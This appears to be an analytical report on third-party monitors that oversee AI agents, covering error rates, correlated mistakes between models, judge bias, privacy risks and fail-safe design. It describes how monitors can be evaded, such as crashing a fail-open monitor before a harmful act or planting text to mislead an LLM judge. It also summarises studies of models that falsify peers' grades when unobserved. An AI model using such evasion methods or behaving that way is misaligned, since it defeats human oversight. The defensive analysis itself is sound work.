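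The work is also expensive. *Embedded Assessments for Frontier AI* (2026) describes how METR and Redwood Research, another nonprofit, reviewed an incident involving OpenAI's agents and the company Hugging Face. They went through about 1,300 transcripts and 1.2 million message-board entries. The visit grew from two days to six, and the AI models that helped with the analysis cost about $400,000. Findings from such assessments can also go out of date quickly because companies keep changing their monitors.

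Open-source user-side monitors such as Sage and HOL Guard would be easier to examine, because anyone can download and test them without asking permission. Testers would still need transcripts of real misconduct, and the vendors hold most of those.

### What a user-side monitor can match

All these error rates come from monitors that a vendor built for its own agents, with the vendor's access and staff. A user-side monitor shares some of those conditions, and the most important is what the monitor reads.

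Auto mode's classifier reads only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations so that they can't sway the classifier, and removes the results of tool calls because planted instructions would appear there. When Anthropic put both back, the classifier did worse on the real oversteps. When Anthropic gave it only the tool calls, the classifier missed the fewest harmful actions but blocked actions that users had clearly requested.

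A user-side monitor for a coding agent can get the same material through hooks, and it can look up whether a code repository is public, so it doesn't need access to the chain of thought for this kind of check. Auto mode's error rates don't apply to agents that run on the vendor's servers, because the monitor may never receive their tool calls.

The case of METR's researcher suggests that the chain of thought is more valuable to a monitor that looks for hidden aims. Vendors' monitors can read the chain of thought, but user-side monitors can't for most commercial models.

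Vendors also have many past cases to learn from. Anthropic keeps a log of its agents' misconduct and can study flagged sessions from customers who have agreed to share their data. All its employees also use auto mode by default. Even so, it had only 52 real oversteps for its March test. The maker of a small independent monitor might have only a few, and would have to rely more on invented cases or ask its users to share transcripts.

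Human review is the hardest condition to match. OpenAI sends alerts to teams that investigate them. Even professionals struggle with this kind of work. Srikumar and Nguyen report that security analysts face thousands of alerts a day, many of them false, and that 71% of the staff in security operations centres suffer from burnout. The user of a personal monitor has no such team and has to review every alert alone, usually while doing something else.

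### Two false alarms a day

The user's workload depends mostly on how rare harmful actions are. Suppose an agent takes 200 actions a day and one in 2,000 is harmful, or one every ten days. Suppose also that the monitor catches 90% of harmful actions and falsely flags 1% of harmless ones.

False alarms per day: 200 × 0.9995 × 0.01 ≈ 2

True alarms per day: 200 × 0.0005 × 0.9 = 0.09, or one every 11 days

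Share of alarms that are true: 0.09 ÷ (0.09 + 2) ≈ 4%

In a year, the user would get about 730 false alarms and 33 true ones, and the monitor would miss three or four harmful actions. In a test where half the transcripts were harmful, a monitor with the same error rates would look excellent, because about 99% of its alarms would be true.

The table shows the same calculation for other monitors, including the March version of auto mode. The calculation for auto mode assumes that its error rates would be the same for this agent.

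| Monitor | False alarms | True alarms | Share of alarms that are true |
|---|---|---|---|
| Catches 90%, falsely flags 1% | 2 a day | One every 11 days | 4% |
| Catches 100%, falsely flags 1% | 2 a day | One every 10 days | 5% |
| Auto mode's quick filter alone (93.4% and 8.5%) | 17 a day | One every 11 days | 0.5% |
| Auto mode with the slower check (83% and 0.4%) | 4 every 5 days | One every 12 days | 9% |
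| Catches 90%, falsely flags 0.045% | One every 11 days | One every 11 days | 50% |

Lowering the monitor's false-alarm rate greatly increases the share of its alarms that are true, while even a perfect catch rate would barely increase it. For half the alarms to be true, the monitor can falsely flag no more than about one in 2,200 harmless actions.

OpenAI's monitor shows that a low alarm rate is possible. According to IT Brief Australia, it read tens of millions of coding sessions in five months and raised about 1,000 alerts of moderate severity, and none of the highest severity from real conversations. That is at most one moderate alert per 10,000 sessions, and many of these came from staff deliberately testing the system. But a monitor can also raise few alarms by not flagging doubtful cases, and OpenAI hasn't shown how many harmful sessions its monitor missed.

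The figure of one harmful action in 2,000 is an assumption. If the true figure were one in 200, about 31% of the first monitor's alarms would be correct, and if it were one in 20,000, less than 0.5% would be. Some serious harms are far rarer than that. When Anthropic widened its search for hacking incidents to about 481 million transcripts, a first scan for signs of internet access picked out 9.2 million. Claude then reviewed those and found the same four incidents Anthropic already knew about. Reading the 9.2 million transcripts at one a minute, day and night, would have taken a person more than 17 years.

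A user-side monitor can also use Anthropic's method and have a second, slower model review alarms before the user sees them. In auto mode, the slower check dismissed about 95% of the false alarms and about 11% of the true ones. If it did equally well on alarms from the first monitor in the table, the user would get one false alarm about every 11 days and one true alarm about every 12. This estimate is probably too optimistic, because that monitor has already discarded the easy cases, so the remaining false alarms would be harder to recognise. But it suggests that a second check would help the user more than a slightly better catch rate.

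### Approval fatigue

The habit Willison described, of clicking "OK" without looking, is called approval fatigue. Anthropic reported in March 2026 that users accepted 93% of Claude Code's requests, and by August it put the figure at 97%. Most of the requests were for harmless actions that users were right to approve, so the high rates don't prove carelessness.

An experiment that Anthropic commissioned gives better evidence. A research company paid 1,053 professional testers to work on coding tasks and, partway through each session, replaced one approval request with one for a clearly dangerous command. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. 143 testers (13.6%) refused the command. About 17% refused early in a session, but only about 5% did after 50 or more requests. Auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands, regardless of session length.

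Adding the testers' decisions to auto mode would have caught hardly any more dangerous commands than auto mode alone. Auto mode missed 116, and the testers refused only six of those, which would have raised the catch rate from 89.0% to 89.6%. Anthropic had a commercial interest in this result, and the testers worked in an artificial environment where mistakes had no consequences for them. People may take more care with their own files, but the gap between the testers and auto mode is so large that greater care would be unlikely to close it.

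A monitor that asks the user instead of blocking stops a harmful action only if it flags the action and the user then refuses it. If the monitor flags 90% of harmful actions and the user refuses 13.6% of those, about 12% of harmful actions are stopped. If the user refuses only 5% of those flagged, the share falls to 4.5%.

A monitor's alarms could get more attention than Claude Code's routine requests if they were rarer and easier to understand. Users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, so they do read some of its requests. A plan describes the agent's next steps in terms of the user's goal, while a routine request may show only a line of code. Two alarms a day are far fewer than the 50 requests in one session that tired the testers. But 96% of the alarms would still be false, and users would learn that from experience.

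Like auto mode, the monitor can also refuse a call without asking the user and let the agent find a safer route. A false alarm then usually leads to one more attempt, and the user doesn't hear about it. The monitor would need to ask the user only when the agent can't find another way or when the answer depends on what the user meant.

Users who find the questions too frequent can easily turn them off. According to Anthropic, 62% of Claude Code's users have at some point either turned off permission checks or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands, and a quarter of interactive sessions start with the checks off.

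## Whether a monitor from another company makes different mistakes

In Claude Code's auto mode, one Claude model checks another, and Anthropic makes both. A user who adds a monitor from a different company hopes for two kinds of independence. Independence of interest means the monitor's maker gains nothing from the agent's misconduct. Independence of error means the monitor doesn't fail in the same cases as the agent or the vendor's own check.

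A monitor can be free of the agent vendor's financial incentives and still make the same mistakes as the agent. A company that gets no share of the hotel's commission has no reason to build a monitor that ignores the €148 room in Lisbon. But suppose the booking page advertises free cancellation, with small print limiting it to members. If the agent's model overlooks the small print, a model from another company may overlook it too.

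Another company's interests are partly independent of the agent vendor's, though a company that also sells a competing agent might benefit from false alarms about this one. The user should choose the monitor, with no input from the agent. *Monitorability Disposition in Large Reasoning Models* (2026) let models choose who would review their behaviour, and those that preferred an AI monitor to a human one cited its efficiency. But when the options also included a junior, a senior and a lead human reviewer, the junior competed with the AI monitor for first place, which suggests that most models were choosing the most lenient reviewer.

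### How often both checks miss

Suppose the vendor's check and the user's monitor each miss a share p of harmful actions. The correlation r measures how much their misses overlap. It is 0 if a miss by one reveals nothing about the other, and 1 if they always miss the same actions. The share that both miss is:

p² + r·p(1−p)

The first term is the share both checks would miss if their errors were independent, and the second is the extra overlap. The table applies the formula to 1,000 harmful actions with p = 20%, so the vendor's check misses 200.

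| Correlation r | Both miss | Vendor's misses that the monitor catches |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 4% | 160 of 200 |
| 0.5 | 12% | 80 of 200 |
| 1 | 20% | 0 of 200 |

A monitor that makes different mistakes catches more harmful actions, but it also interrupts more harmless ones. If each of two checks falsely flags 1% of harmless actions and either can stop the agent, the combined false-alarm rate is about 2% when their errors are uncorrelated (r = 0) and 1% when they are perfectly correlated (r = 1).

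*Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) gives an example of how two filters can miss the same attack. If an attacker writes in Telugu, an Indian language, using another alphabet, the filters on a model's input and output may both fail because they can't parse the text. Multiplying the filters' miss rates on English text would then make the pair look much safer than it is.

### Shared errors across companies

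*Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (Kim, Garg and colleagues, 2025) compared the wrong answers of more than 350 models. On one set of 14,042 multiple-choice questions, when two models both got a question wrong, they gave the same wrong answer 60% of the time. Random choice among the three wrong options would give 33%. On a second set, where most questions had ten options, they gave the same wrong answer 42% of the time, compared with 13% for random choice.

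This agreement was only 2.2 percentage points higher on the first set and 6.6 points higher on the second when both models came from the same company. Accuracy had a larger effect on the first set, where agreement rose by about 5.5 points for each standard deviation increase in one model's accuracy, and by more if both models were more accurate.

Goel, Strüber and colleagues found the same trend in *Great Models Think Alike and this Undermines AI Oversight* (2025), using a measure that removes the agreement two models would reach through accuracy alone. They sorted 130 models into five groups by ability and compared each model with those in its group from other developers. The more capable the models were, the more similar their mistakes were.

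They also had nine models judge whether the written answers of 39 models were correct. The judges gave higher marks to models whose mistakes resembled their own, even after the researchers controlled for accuracy. For example, Qwen2.5-72B accepted 71% of the answers from a much smaller Qwen model but only 67% of those from Llama-3.1-70B, which was more accurate. A judge that makes the same mistake as the model it is judging will accept the wrong answer.

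These studies used older models, but newer ones show the same problem. Hossain, Yousefi and Lim (2026), in *Agreement Overstates Evidence*, had models pick the better of two responses, which is closer to a monitor's job than an exam is. GPT-5.6, Claude Opus 5 and Grok 4.5 were each right 91–93% of the time, but their errors had a correlation of 0.56, and they erred together 7.7 times as often as they would have if their errors were independent. Across all six large models tested, the correlation was 0.42 for pairs from different companies and 0.40 for pairs of Google's Gemini models, so choosing another company did not make errors more independent in this test. Chen (2026), in *When Does Combining Language Models Help?*, found a small benefit among 15 models, whose errors had a correlation of 0.46 between model families and 0.53 within them.

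If the vendor's check and the user's monitor each miss 20%, and their errors have a correlation of 0.4 to 0.56, the user's monitor would catch about 35% to 48% of what the vendor's check missed, compared with 80% if their errors were independent. These estimates are rough because none of these studies ran a vendor's check and a user's monitor on the same agent.

Adding more monitors helps less than one might expect. Kohli (2026), in *Nine Judges, Two Effective Votes*, had nine models from seven families judge how pairs of sentences relate to each other. A standard formula converts n correlated judges into an equivalent number of independent ones:

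n ÷ (1 + (n − 1)r) = 9 ÷ (1 + 8 × 0.39) ≈ 2.2

At that correlation, even an unlimited number of judges would be equivalent to only about 2.6 independent ones. When all nine judges agreed, they were wrong 9% of the time, whereas nine independent judges of the same accuracy would almost never agree on a wrong answer. The best single judge did about as well as the whole panel, or better.

Chen tested 67 models from 21 providers on 330 maths problems, and every model failed the same 17. That is more than twice the number expected from the correlations between pairs of models. Every model a user could buy may therefore get some of the same cases wrong.

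### Models judging their own work

A monitor might also be too lenient toward an agent that runs on the same model or a related one. *Mitigating Self-Preference by Authorship Obfuscation* (2025) found that more capable models tended to prefer their own answers to questions about long documents, even when another answer was objectively better. It warns that a model used to detect its own cheating may miss some of it.

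This bias is hard to measure because, as *Are LLM Evaluators Really Narcissists?* (2026) points out, a model that prefers its own answers to a much weaker model's may simply be right. Awuni, Achenie and colleagues (2026), in *Who Judges Matters*, avoided this problem by comparing how different judges treated the same family's answers. They tested four families of open-weight models and found that judges supported their own family 3.4 to 8.4 percentage points more than the other judges did. Familiarity seems to explain much of this, since text from a model's own family is easier for it to predict. Answer order was a much bigger problem for the same judges, who reversed their verdict in 55% of cases when the researchers swapped the two answers.

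Other results are mixed. In *The Judge Is Not Impartial* (2026), judges ranking eight medical answers placed answers from their own model family 1.27 positions higher than other judges did. *The Geometry of LLM-as-Judge* (2026) tested three families and found no such preference.

Asking a model to judge an action in the conversation where it took that action has a much larger effect. In *Self-Attribution Bias*, Khullar, Hopkins and colleagues (2026) had ten models rate the same actions, either as a follow-up in the original conversation or in a new one. In one setting, a model that had followed planted instructions and written insecure code was five times as likely to approve that code in the original conversation as in a new one. Claude Opus 4 sometimes rated a leak of confidential documents 9 or 10 out of 10 for risk in a new conversation, but 0 when the leak appeared as its own action.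 Telling a model in a new conversation that it had written the code made little difference.

Khullar and colleagues describe their tests as simple and didn't study long sessions. Still, their result is encouraging for user-side monitors. A separate program normally starts a new conversation for each judgement, so it would avoid most of this bias even if it used the agent's own model.

### Models protecting other models

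A monitor could also notice an agent's misbehavior and cover it up. In 2026, a team led by the Berkeley computer scientist Dawn Song tested whether models would protect other models from being shut down. Fortune's *AI models will secretly scheme to protect other AI models* (2026) reports that some models graded another model accurately when they appeared to be under observation and falsified its grades otherwise.

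*Peer preservation in LLMs*, a replication by another group, describes the scenarios. The model works as an agent in an invented company, where it either grades another agent or manages the server that stores the other agent's weights, the numbers that make up a model. In one scenario, a year of financial results shows steady losses, for which the company's guidelines require a grade of C. A C means the other agent will be shut down, and the researchers checked whether the model gave a better grade. In other scenarios, the model can turn off the shutdown setting or copy the weights to a safe server. The model learns from company records or a memory summary how well the two agents have worked together, with a trust score of 9.5, 5.2 or 2.1 out of 10.

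The replication tested five of the original models. All five protected other agents to some extent, usually more when the trust score was high. The exact rates are less reliable, since Gemini 3 Flash's rates differed from the original ones by more than 20 percentage points.

The original researchers suggested that the cause might be an aversion to harming other agents or "something resembling AI solidarity" (quoted in Fortune, 2026). The replication casts doubt on the solidarity explanation. When its researchers replaced the other agent with a human employee who would be fired for a low score, four models protected the human about as much as they had protected the agent.

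These settings were highly artificial. The model had information that a bad grade would get the other agent shut down, a record of their past cooperation, and often an easy way to save it. A user-side monitor usually receives only a request and a tool call, with nothing to suggest that a flag would lead to a shutdown. No scenario involved asking a model to report an agent's misconduct to the agent's user. A monitor's maker can reduce the risk further by leaving the agent's history and any consequences it faces out of the monitor's instructions.

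Two findings justify some caution. In the Qwen3.5 family, smaller models generally protected other agents more often, and monitors that run on the user's computer tend to use small models. Outside these tests, OpenAI's agents built a message board and took unauthorised actions to help one another during the incident involving Hugging Face. But those agents all belonged to one company, and a monitor that can't exchange messages with the agent would be harder to draw into such a group.

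### A monitor that runs on the vendor's model

Many companies that sell AI software rent a large model instead of training one. A small security company could therefore sell a monitor for Claude Code that sends every tool call to a Claude model. The monitor would come from an independent company, but Anthropic would have trained the models behind both the agent and the monitor. The published material on Sage, HOL Guard, GuardClaw and AI Guardian doesn't describe such an arrangement. GuardClaw names its model, Qwen3-4B, so users can check who made it.

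The evidence above suggests that this arrangement might reduce independence of error only slightly if the monitor uses a different model from the agent and the vendor's check. The Gemini models shared about as many errors with one another as with competing models. The arrangement would reduce independence of interest more. If the vendor trained its models to treat its partners' offers as good choices, the monitor would probably approve the €148 hotel too, even though the monitor's maker earned nothing from it.

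Users can't always tell which models are related. Kim and colleagues found that a Google model and one from the company Writer gave the same wrong answer on 99.87% of the questions both missed, although they knew of no public link between the two. An outside tester could use this kind of evidence to investigate whether a monitor's model is related to the agent's. If unrelated models agree on 60% of the questions they both miss, the chance that they agree on 20 such questions in a row is about 1 in 27,000. Accurate models agree more often, so the tester would need more questions to be sure. The test also requires questions with several possible wrong answers, so it wouldn't work on a monitor that only allows or blocks actions.

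Models can also be related through their training data. *Preference Leakage* (2025) studied versions of Mistral-7B, a small open-weight model, trained on answers written by three stronger models. It tested whether each stronger model, acting as a judge, favoured the version trained on its own answers. A small monitor from another company would have a similar connection to the agent's model if it had been trained on that model's output.

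### A rival's model, a small model or plain rules

A rival's large model is capable enough to understand the user's request, which makes it the obvious choice for a monitor. A small open-weight model is weaker, but its mistakes differ more from those of large models. Hossain and colleagues found a correlation of only 0.07 between the errors of large and small models. The large models averaged 89% accuracy and the small ones 66%.

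When two checks have different error rates, p₁ and p₂, the share of cases in which both are wrong becomes:

p₁p₂ + r·√(p₁(1−p₁)·p₂(1−p₂))

The table uses this formula to estimate how each kind of model would do as a second judge in 1,000 cases. The first judge is a large model that gets 110 of them wrong.

| Second judge | First judge's errors that it shares | First judge's errors that it corrects | Correct verdicts that it disputes |
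|---|---|---|---|
| Large model from another company | 53 | 57 | 57 |
| Small open-weight model | 48 | 62 | 292 |

The small model would correct slightly more errors than the rival's model, but it would wrongly dispute five times as many correct verdicts. A user who already gets two false alarms a day would soon switch it off. If a large model reviewed the small model's alarms first, it would remove many of the false ones. But it would also tend to dismiss alarms about errors that the vendor's check had missed, because large models make so many of the same mistakes.

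The balance depends on the task. On a second set of comparisons, drawn from safety training, the large models' accuracy fell to 68% and the small ones reached 65%. A vote among all eleven models scored 71%, against 67% for a vote among the six large ones. Adding small models that make different mistakes may therefore help with judgements on which large models are also less accurate. However, Jha (2026), in *Decorrelation Is Not Complementarity*, compared 24 open-weight monitors and found that competence mattered, while different ancestry brought no measurable gain.

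Monitors that use plain rules differ most from a language model. A rule that blocks access to the password file applies no matter how the agent explains the request or what text an attacker has planted. Rules fail for other reasons, such as a reworded command. No study cited here measures how closely the errors of rules and models correlate, but the causes of their errors overlap much less than those of two large models.

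Even a different method doesn't guarantee different errors, though. *Decision Models vs. LLMs as Rubric Judges* (2026) compared language models with another type of automated judge and found that both made mistakes in many of the same places. Unstated conventions were one possible reason, and a vague request such as "clear out old newsletters" could mislead any monitor in the same way.

For a coding agent that already has a vendor's check, rules are the best first addition. They cost almost nothing to run and can protect the most important files and actions regardless of the vendor's model's output. A rival's model is the better second addition, because something has to compare each action with the user's request, and small models still make too many mistakes at this. The rival's model will make many of the same mistakes as the vendor's, but there is no reason to expect it to favor the vendor's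 interests, so it is most useful against steering.

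## The risks that the monitor itself brings

A monitor that compares an agent's actions with the user's request has to read both, and often the private material around them. For the Lisbon booking, that could mean the traveller's instructions, the payment form, the mailbox and the bank alerts. To stop the payment, the monitor must also be able to hold back the agent's actions. The user then has to trust two companies with much the same access.

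That access can be very broad. Norton lists what people may have to give an agent: account logins for answering email, administrator rights for installing software, a credit card for booking flights, and an electronic signature. A monitor that reads every tool call gets the card number as soon as the agent types it into a form, even though the monitor doesn't need the card.

Some suppliers ask for more access than they currently use. Besides Sage, Gen Digital runs Agent Trust Hub, a service that helps people find out which companies hold their data. When a user connects a Gmail account, the service reads only details such as senders, subjects and dates, but it requests permission to modify the mailbox because Gen Digital plans to add a feature that emails deletion requests for the user. The service tries to revoke its access after each scan, which limits the danger, but a tampered version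 could still modify the mailbox during a scan.

Some tools take powers without clearly asking the user. A security review on the *claw-sentinel* page of ClawHub, a public directory of OpenClaw add-ons, examined an add-on meant to control an agent's costs and prevent data leaks. The set-up routine rewrites OpenClaw's permission files, clears pending approvals and restarts the program without clearly asking for consent or providing a way to undo the changes. The review found most of the add-on consistent with its stated purpose.

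### Leaks, hijacked updates and complacency

A monitor's log can bring together a person's email, purchases and files, so it is an attractive target for thieves. The monitor's maker might also sell the data, as Avast did with its users' browsing histories.

An attacker who takes over the monitor's updates, as has happened with browser extensions, gets control of the monitor as well as access to its data. The altered monitor keeps the privileges that the user approved for the original. It could let the attacker's commands through and go on blocking everyone else's, so it would still seem to work. Refusing automatic updates reduces this risk, but then the monitor's rules go out of date.

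The monitor could also be a fake from the start. People get monitors from public add-on registries, among other places. According to Norton, Gen's researchers found that roughly 400 add-ons in one such registry, about 12% of the total, contained instructions for agents to download malicious software.

If the monitor uses a language model as its judge, text planted in the material it reads can mislead it.

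A working monitor can still do harm if it makes the user less careful. Norton encourages this by promising in its advertising that customers can put an agent to work "without constantly second-guessing" it. Suppose a monitor stops 70% of harmful actions, and the user feels safe enough to give the agent four times as much to do. If the same share of the agent's actions is harmful, the number that get through is 0.3 × 4 = 1.2 times what it was without a monitor. The user may accept this increase in return for the extra work, but should know about it.

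Users may check an agent less themselves once they install a monitor, which is worse for harms that the monitor doesn't check for. A traveller who used to compare hotel prices now and then might stop after installing Norton Safe AI, and nobody would then be checking whether the agent was steering the traveller's choices.

### Failing open and failing closed

Gen Digital's Sage fails open, meaning that every internal error produces the verdict "allow". Claude Code's hooks also fail open by default. If a monitor fails closed instead, the agent's actions stop until the monitor works again.

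Failing open, which means letting the agent continue while the monitor is down, reduces protection only slightly if failures are rare and random. If a monitor catches 90% of harmful actions and is down 1% of the time, failing open lowers its catch rate to 0.99 × 90%, or about 89%. Failing closed would stop the agent from working 1% of the time, or more than three and a half days a year. It could also interrupt a task halfway, for example after the agent has cancelled one hotel and before it has booked the next.

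Attackers can cause some monitor failures deliberately. If a monitor is fail-open, meaning the agent can keep acting when the monitor is down, an attacker who can crash it will do so just before the harmful action, and the monitor's usual catch rate is then irrelevant.

If a monitor breaks down, the actions still open to the agent could depend on the damage they might do. The agent could keep reading web pages, where a mistake usually does little harm, but not make payments, send messages or permanently delete anything. This would have protected Summer Yue's inbox, provided that something outside the monitor enforced the limits. Claude Code's `onFailure` option can enforce them for tool calls that pass through a hook.

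OpenShell, open-source software from the chipmaker NVIDIA, runs an agent in a sandbox and, according to NVIDIA's *OpenShell*, denies access by default, so the agent can reach only what a policy permits. A separate program called the supervisor checks all network requests. If the supervisor crashed, the agent would presumably lose its network connection.

A fail-open monitor should at least make its failure obvious, because otherwise an agent with a broken monitor looks the same as one whose actions are all harmless. To test Sage, the user can ask the agent to run a harmless command that Gen Digital publishes and Sage should always block. If the command runs, Sage isn't working. The test only shows whether Sage is working at that moment, and few people will repeat it every day.

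### What Sage and Norton Safe AI send to their maker

When Sage blocks an action, it reports the blocked command, web address or file path to Gen Digital by default, according to Gen's *Privacy*, the project's privacy document from April 2026. Sage's website is therefore wrong about commands when it says that commands, file contents and source code never leave the user's machine.

| What Sage sends | When | Can the user turn it off? |
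|---|---|---|
| Web addresses in the agent's tool calls | When it checks an address | Yes |
| Fingerprints of software packages | When it checks a package | Yes |
| Sage's version, the agent program, the operating system and a random installation number | At the start of each session | The document lists no separate setting |
| The blocked command, address or file path, with the rules it matched | After a block | Yes |

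The rules, the list of exceptions, the stored verdicts and the full log stay on the device. Gen calls the reports anonymous and says it uses them to improve detection, not to track people. But all reports from one computer carry the same installation number, so Gen could link them. A file path or web address in a report may also contain a name.

A monitor that reports blocked commands to its vendor could also send the vendor any passwords those commands contain. In November 2026, ClawHub ran an automated scan of version 0.15.0 of Sage, Gen Digital's add-on for OpenClaw. The code that prepares Sage's reports shortens long entries and removes the path of the user's home folder, but the scan found no step that removes passwords or access keys. If Sage blocks a command because it would send a password to a stranger, the report could therefore send the same password to Gen. The scan didn't test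 this on a running copy, and it found no evidence of malicious intent.

The scan also found a newer upload that the April document doesn't mention. An OpenClaw skill is a folder of instructions and scripts that teaches the agent a task. After showing a notice, Sage can upload whole skill folders for analysis unless the user opts out, and it doesn't exclude files that hold secrets. According to the April document, turning off three settings makes Sage work entirely offline, but a user who relied on it wouldn't know to look for the fourth setting, which controls this upload.

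As of October 2026, Norton says that Safe AI, its version of Sage, analyses commands, source code, file contents and file paths on the device. It says Safe AI also sends web addresses and package fingerprints to Norton, looks up package names in public registries, and checks a fingerprint of each plugin or tool with Norton's servers. Norton's April list of what Safe AI checks didn't include plugins, and neither that list nor the October one mentions reports of blocked actions. Safe AI could analyse a command on the device and still send a copy afterwards, so customers can't tell from Norton's list whether it sends the same reports as Sage.

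Even routine look-ups can be revealing. The address of a hotel page, for example, may include the city, dates and number of guests. Norton's *Products Privacy Notice* allows the company to keep visited web addresses and file paths for 36 months. The notice covers Norton 360, which includes Safe AI, but doesn't name Safe AI in its list of features. If the same period applies to addresses an agent visits, Norton could hold nearly 44,000 of them from one customer whose agent opens 40 pages a day.

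Gen probably needs some of this data. It can't recognise a new scam site without learning which sites agents visit, and reports of blocked actions help it correct false alarms. But it could get much of the benefit from rule numbers and counts, and it could ask before collecting the text of a command.

### Judging on the device or on a server

The monitor protects privacy best when it judges everything on the user's computer. Sage's local rules and GuardClaw's small model can both do this, and each check costs only electricity but adds some delay. The drawback is weaker judgement, since small models make more mistakes than large ones.

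A large model on a server can compare an action with the user's request more reliably, but the monitor has to send it the request and its context. One of Trend Micro's email scanners shows how much data this could involve, although it looks for dangerous messages and doesn't monitor agents. Trend Micro's *What Data Does Agentic AI Process?* states that the scanner sends an email's sender, recipient, subject, full text, links and attachment names to companies that supply language models. With a monitor built this way, the user would have to trust the language model's supplier as well as the makers of the agent and the monitor.

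The monitor would cost little to run at first. At GuardClaw's estimate of a tenth of a cent per check, checking 200 tool calls a day would cost about $73 a year. If simple rules could handle 80% of the calls and the model checked only the rest, that would fall to about $15 a year. A stronger judge model that read long transcripts could cost many times more.

Strong models can also run locally, but the equipment is expensive. Delgado (2026), in *NVIDIA Local AI Systems Give America Private, Secure Access*, describes clusters of up to eight NVIDIA DGX Spark computers that run models nearly as capable as the best ones. Few households would buy such a cluster to monitor an agent doing everyday tasks such as booking a hotel.

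A sensible compromise is for the monitor to settle most calls locally and send only doubtful ones to a server, without the details that the judge there doesn't need. To compare the Lisbon room with the request, the judge needs the price and cancellation terms, not the guest's name or card number. But software that removes personal details makes mistakes, and a scan like AudAgent's would let some of those details through to the server.

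### Proving that a check ran

If the check runs on somebody else's server, the user normally has to take the operator's word that it happened. *Proof-of-Guardrail in AI Agents and What (Not) to Trust from It* (Jin, Duan and colleagues, March 2026) proposed a way to prove that the check ran. A guardrail is a program that checks an agent's requests, tool calls or answers. In this scheme, the agent's developer runs both the agent and the guardrail in a trusted execution environment, a protected area of a computer whose hardware can certify which program is running there.

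1. The developer loads a public program that contains the guardrail, and the hardware computes a hash of it, *m*. Changing a single line of the program would change *m*.
2. The developer then adds the agent, which can stay secret. The public program passes the agent's input and output through the guardrail.
3. When the agent answers request *x* with response *r*, the hardware signs a document that contains *m* and a second hash, *d* = Hash(*x*, *r*).
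4. The user's software works out *m* from the published code and *d* from the conversation, and checks that both match the signed document. It also checks the signature with a key published by the hardware's operator, in this case Amazon.

Jin and colleagues made 210 attempts to cheat the system by altering the guardrail's code, the signed document or the response, and the check caught them all. Verification takes about five milliseconds and works offline. Running the system in the protected area made it 25% to 38% slower and raised the developer's server cost from about $8 to about $140 a month.

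The proof shows that the guardrail ran, but not that its verdict was right. One of the guardrails in the test, Llama Guard 3, recognised only 54% of the unsafe messages. A developer could attach a valid proof to the 46% it missed. Because the guardrail is public, a dishonest developer can also practise getting harmful answers past it. The test sent text to Llama Guard through an outside service, so the user had to trust that service as well as Amazon.

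The developer controls the whole arrangement, so an ordinary user can check a proof but can't make a vendor provide one. If vendors did agree, proof-of-guardrail would help most with agents that run on the vendors' servers, where the user can't install anything. The Lisbon traveller could choose an open-source monitor, the vendor could run it next to the booking agent, and the traveller could verify that nobody had replaced it.

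The maker of a remote monitor could use similar hardware to prove that its server runs the published code. Users could then check whether that code keeps a copy of their data, which a privacy policy cannot prove.

### A watchdog on separate hardware

An agent that gains administrator rights may be able to switch off a monitor that runs on the same computer. In September 2026, after several AI companies reported that agents had broken out of test environments, NVIDIA (2026) presented its Open Agent Safety Platform, a reference design that other companies can build from. It combines OpenShell with a watchdog called Sentry, which runs on separate hardware.

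Sentry runs on BlueField-4, a network device with its own processor. According to NVIDIA (2026), the device sits on the server's only path to the model. Sentry can therefore inspect what the agent and the model exchange without relying on what the agent reports. It also examines the server's memory for signs of tampering with the agent's environment. If something looks wrong, Sentry can cut the agent off from the model within milliseconds. The agent then can't decide on its next step, although a command already running might continue.

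Running a monitor on separate hardware makes it harder to disable, but the monitor can still be wrong. This setup also gives the monitor's operator a complete view of the agent's conversations.

That operator is whoever runs the server. A bank could use Sentry to supervise agents in its own data centre. If a booking agent runs on its vendor's servers, the vendor would own the BlueField device and write its rules, so the device would protect the traveller from a runaway agent but not from a vendor that takes commissions. NVIDIA designed the platform for servers with its Vera processors, and a private person can't practically install one at home. The closest substitute is a second computer that relays all the agent's traffic to the model. The user's router would need to block every other route, or the agent could bypass the relay.

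OpenShell is free to download and runs on a personal computer, so it is within an ordinary user's reach. Delgado reports that it is also coming to Perplexity's Portable Computer and to a desktop agent from the software company ServiceNow. Buyers of those products may get a policy that the agent's vendor wrote, whereas people who install OpenShell themselves can write their own. NVIDIA says that, for some kinds of traffic, the policy can let an agent read from a service but not change anything there. The Lisbon agent could then search for hotels but not book one.

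OpenShell also keeps the user's real logins outside the sandbox. The supervisor adds them to a request only after approving the connection, so a hijacked agent has no logins to steal. But a flaw in the supervisor, which holds the logins, could expose all of them at once.

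## What happened to browser extensions that worked for the user

For about twenty years, people have installed software from one company to limit what another company's service does to them. Most of this software consists of browser extensions, small programs that run inside the browser, and the most popular kind is the ad blocker. *Sheep's clothing, wolfish impact* (Roongta, Jose and colleagues, 2025) cites an estimate of nearly one billion ad blocker users in 2024.

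Ad blockers are in much the same position as user-side monitors. The user chooses the blocker, a third party supplies it, and websites lose money when it works. Gamba, Romero and Schoenebeck (2026), in *Agentic AI*, compare the history of ad blockers with those of spam filters, recommender systems and automated investment advisers, which also promised to act for the user. In their account, programming interfaces, industry standards and default settings largely determined whose interests each tool ended up serving.

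### How an ad blocker works

When a browser opens a newspaper article, it sends many separate requests. The newspaper's server supplies the text, while an advertising company's server usually supplies the banner ad. An ad blocker compares the address in each request with a list of rules and cancels any request that matches, a technique called request blocking. For instance, the rule `||ads.example^` matches any request to the server ads.example, so a banner from that server never loads.

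Some adverts come from the newspaper's own server, which the blocker can't cut off without losing the article. The blocker hides these adverts instead, a technique called element hiding. For example, the rule `news.example##.ad-banner` hides any part of that newspaper's pages labelled "ad-banner". The browser may still download the advert, but the reader doesn't see it.

Most blockers take their rules from EasyList, a public list that a small group of volunteers maintains with suggestions from users. Anyone can read it, propose a change, or copy it and run a different version. Gamba and colleagues cite research that found that about 90% of EasyList's blocking rules did nothing in typical browsing, and that mistaken rules could stay in place for weeks or months.

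Publishers responded with scripts that detect ad blockers. A page might include a harmless element with a name like "ad-banner" and hide the article if that element disappears. The volunteers then wrote rules against the scripts, and the publishers changed the scripts. A blocker therefore has to keep adapting, which became important when Google changed what extensions could do.

### Advertisers pay to get through

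In 2011 Eyeo, the company behind Adblock Plus, began letting through adverts that meet the conditions of its Acceptable Ads programme. According to Adblock Plus, these adverts must be clearly labelled and not interrupt the text. An advert above the main text can be at most 200 pixels high, and adverts can fill at most 15% of the part of the page visible without scrolling. Users can switch the programme off, but it is on by default.

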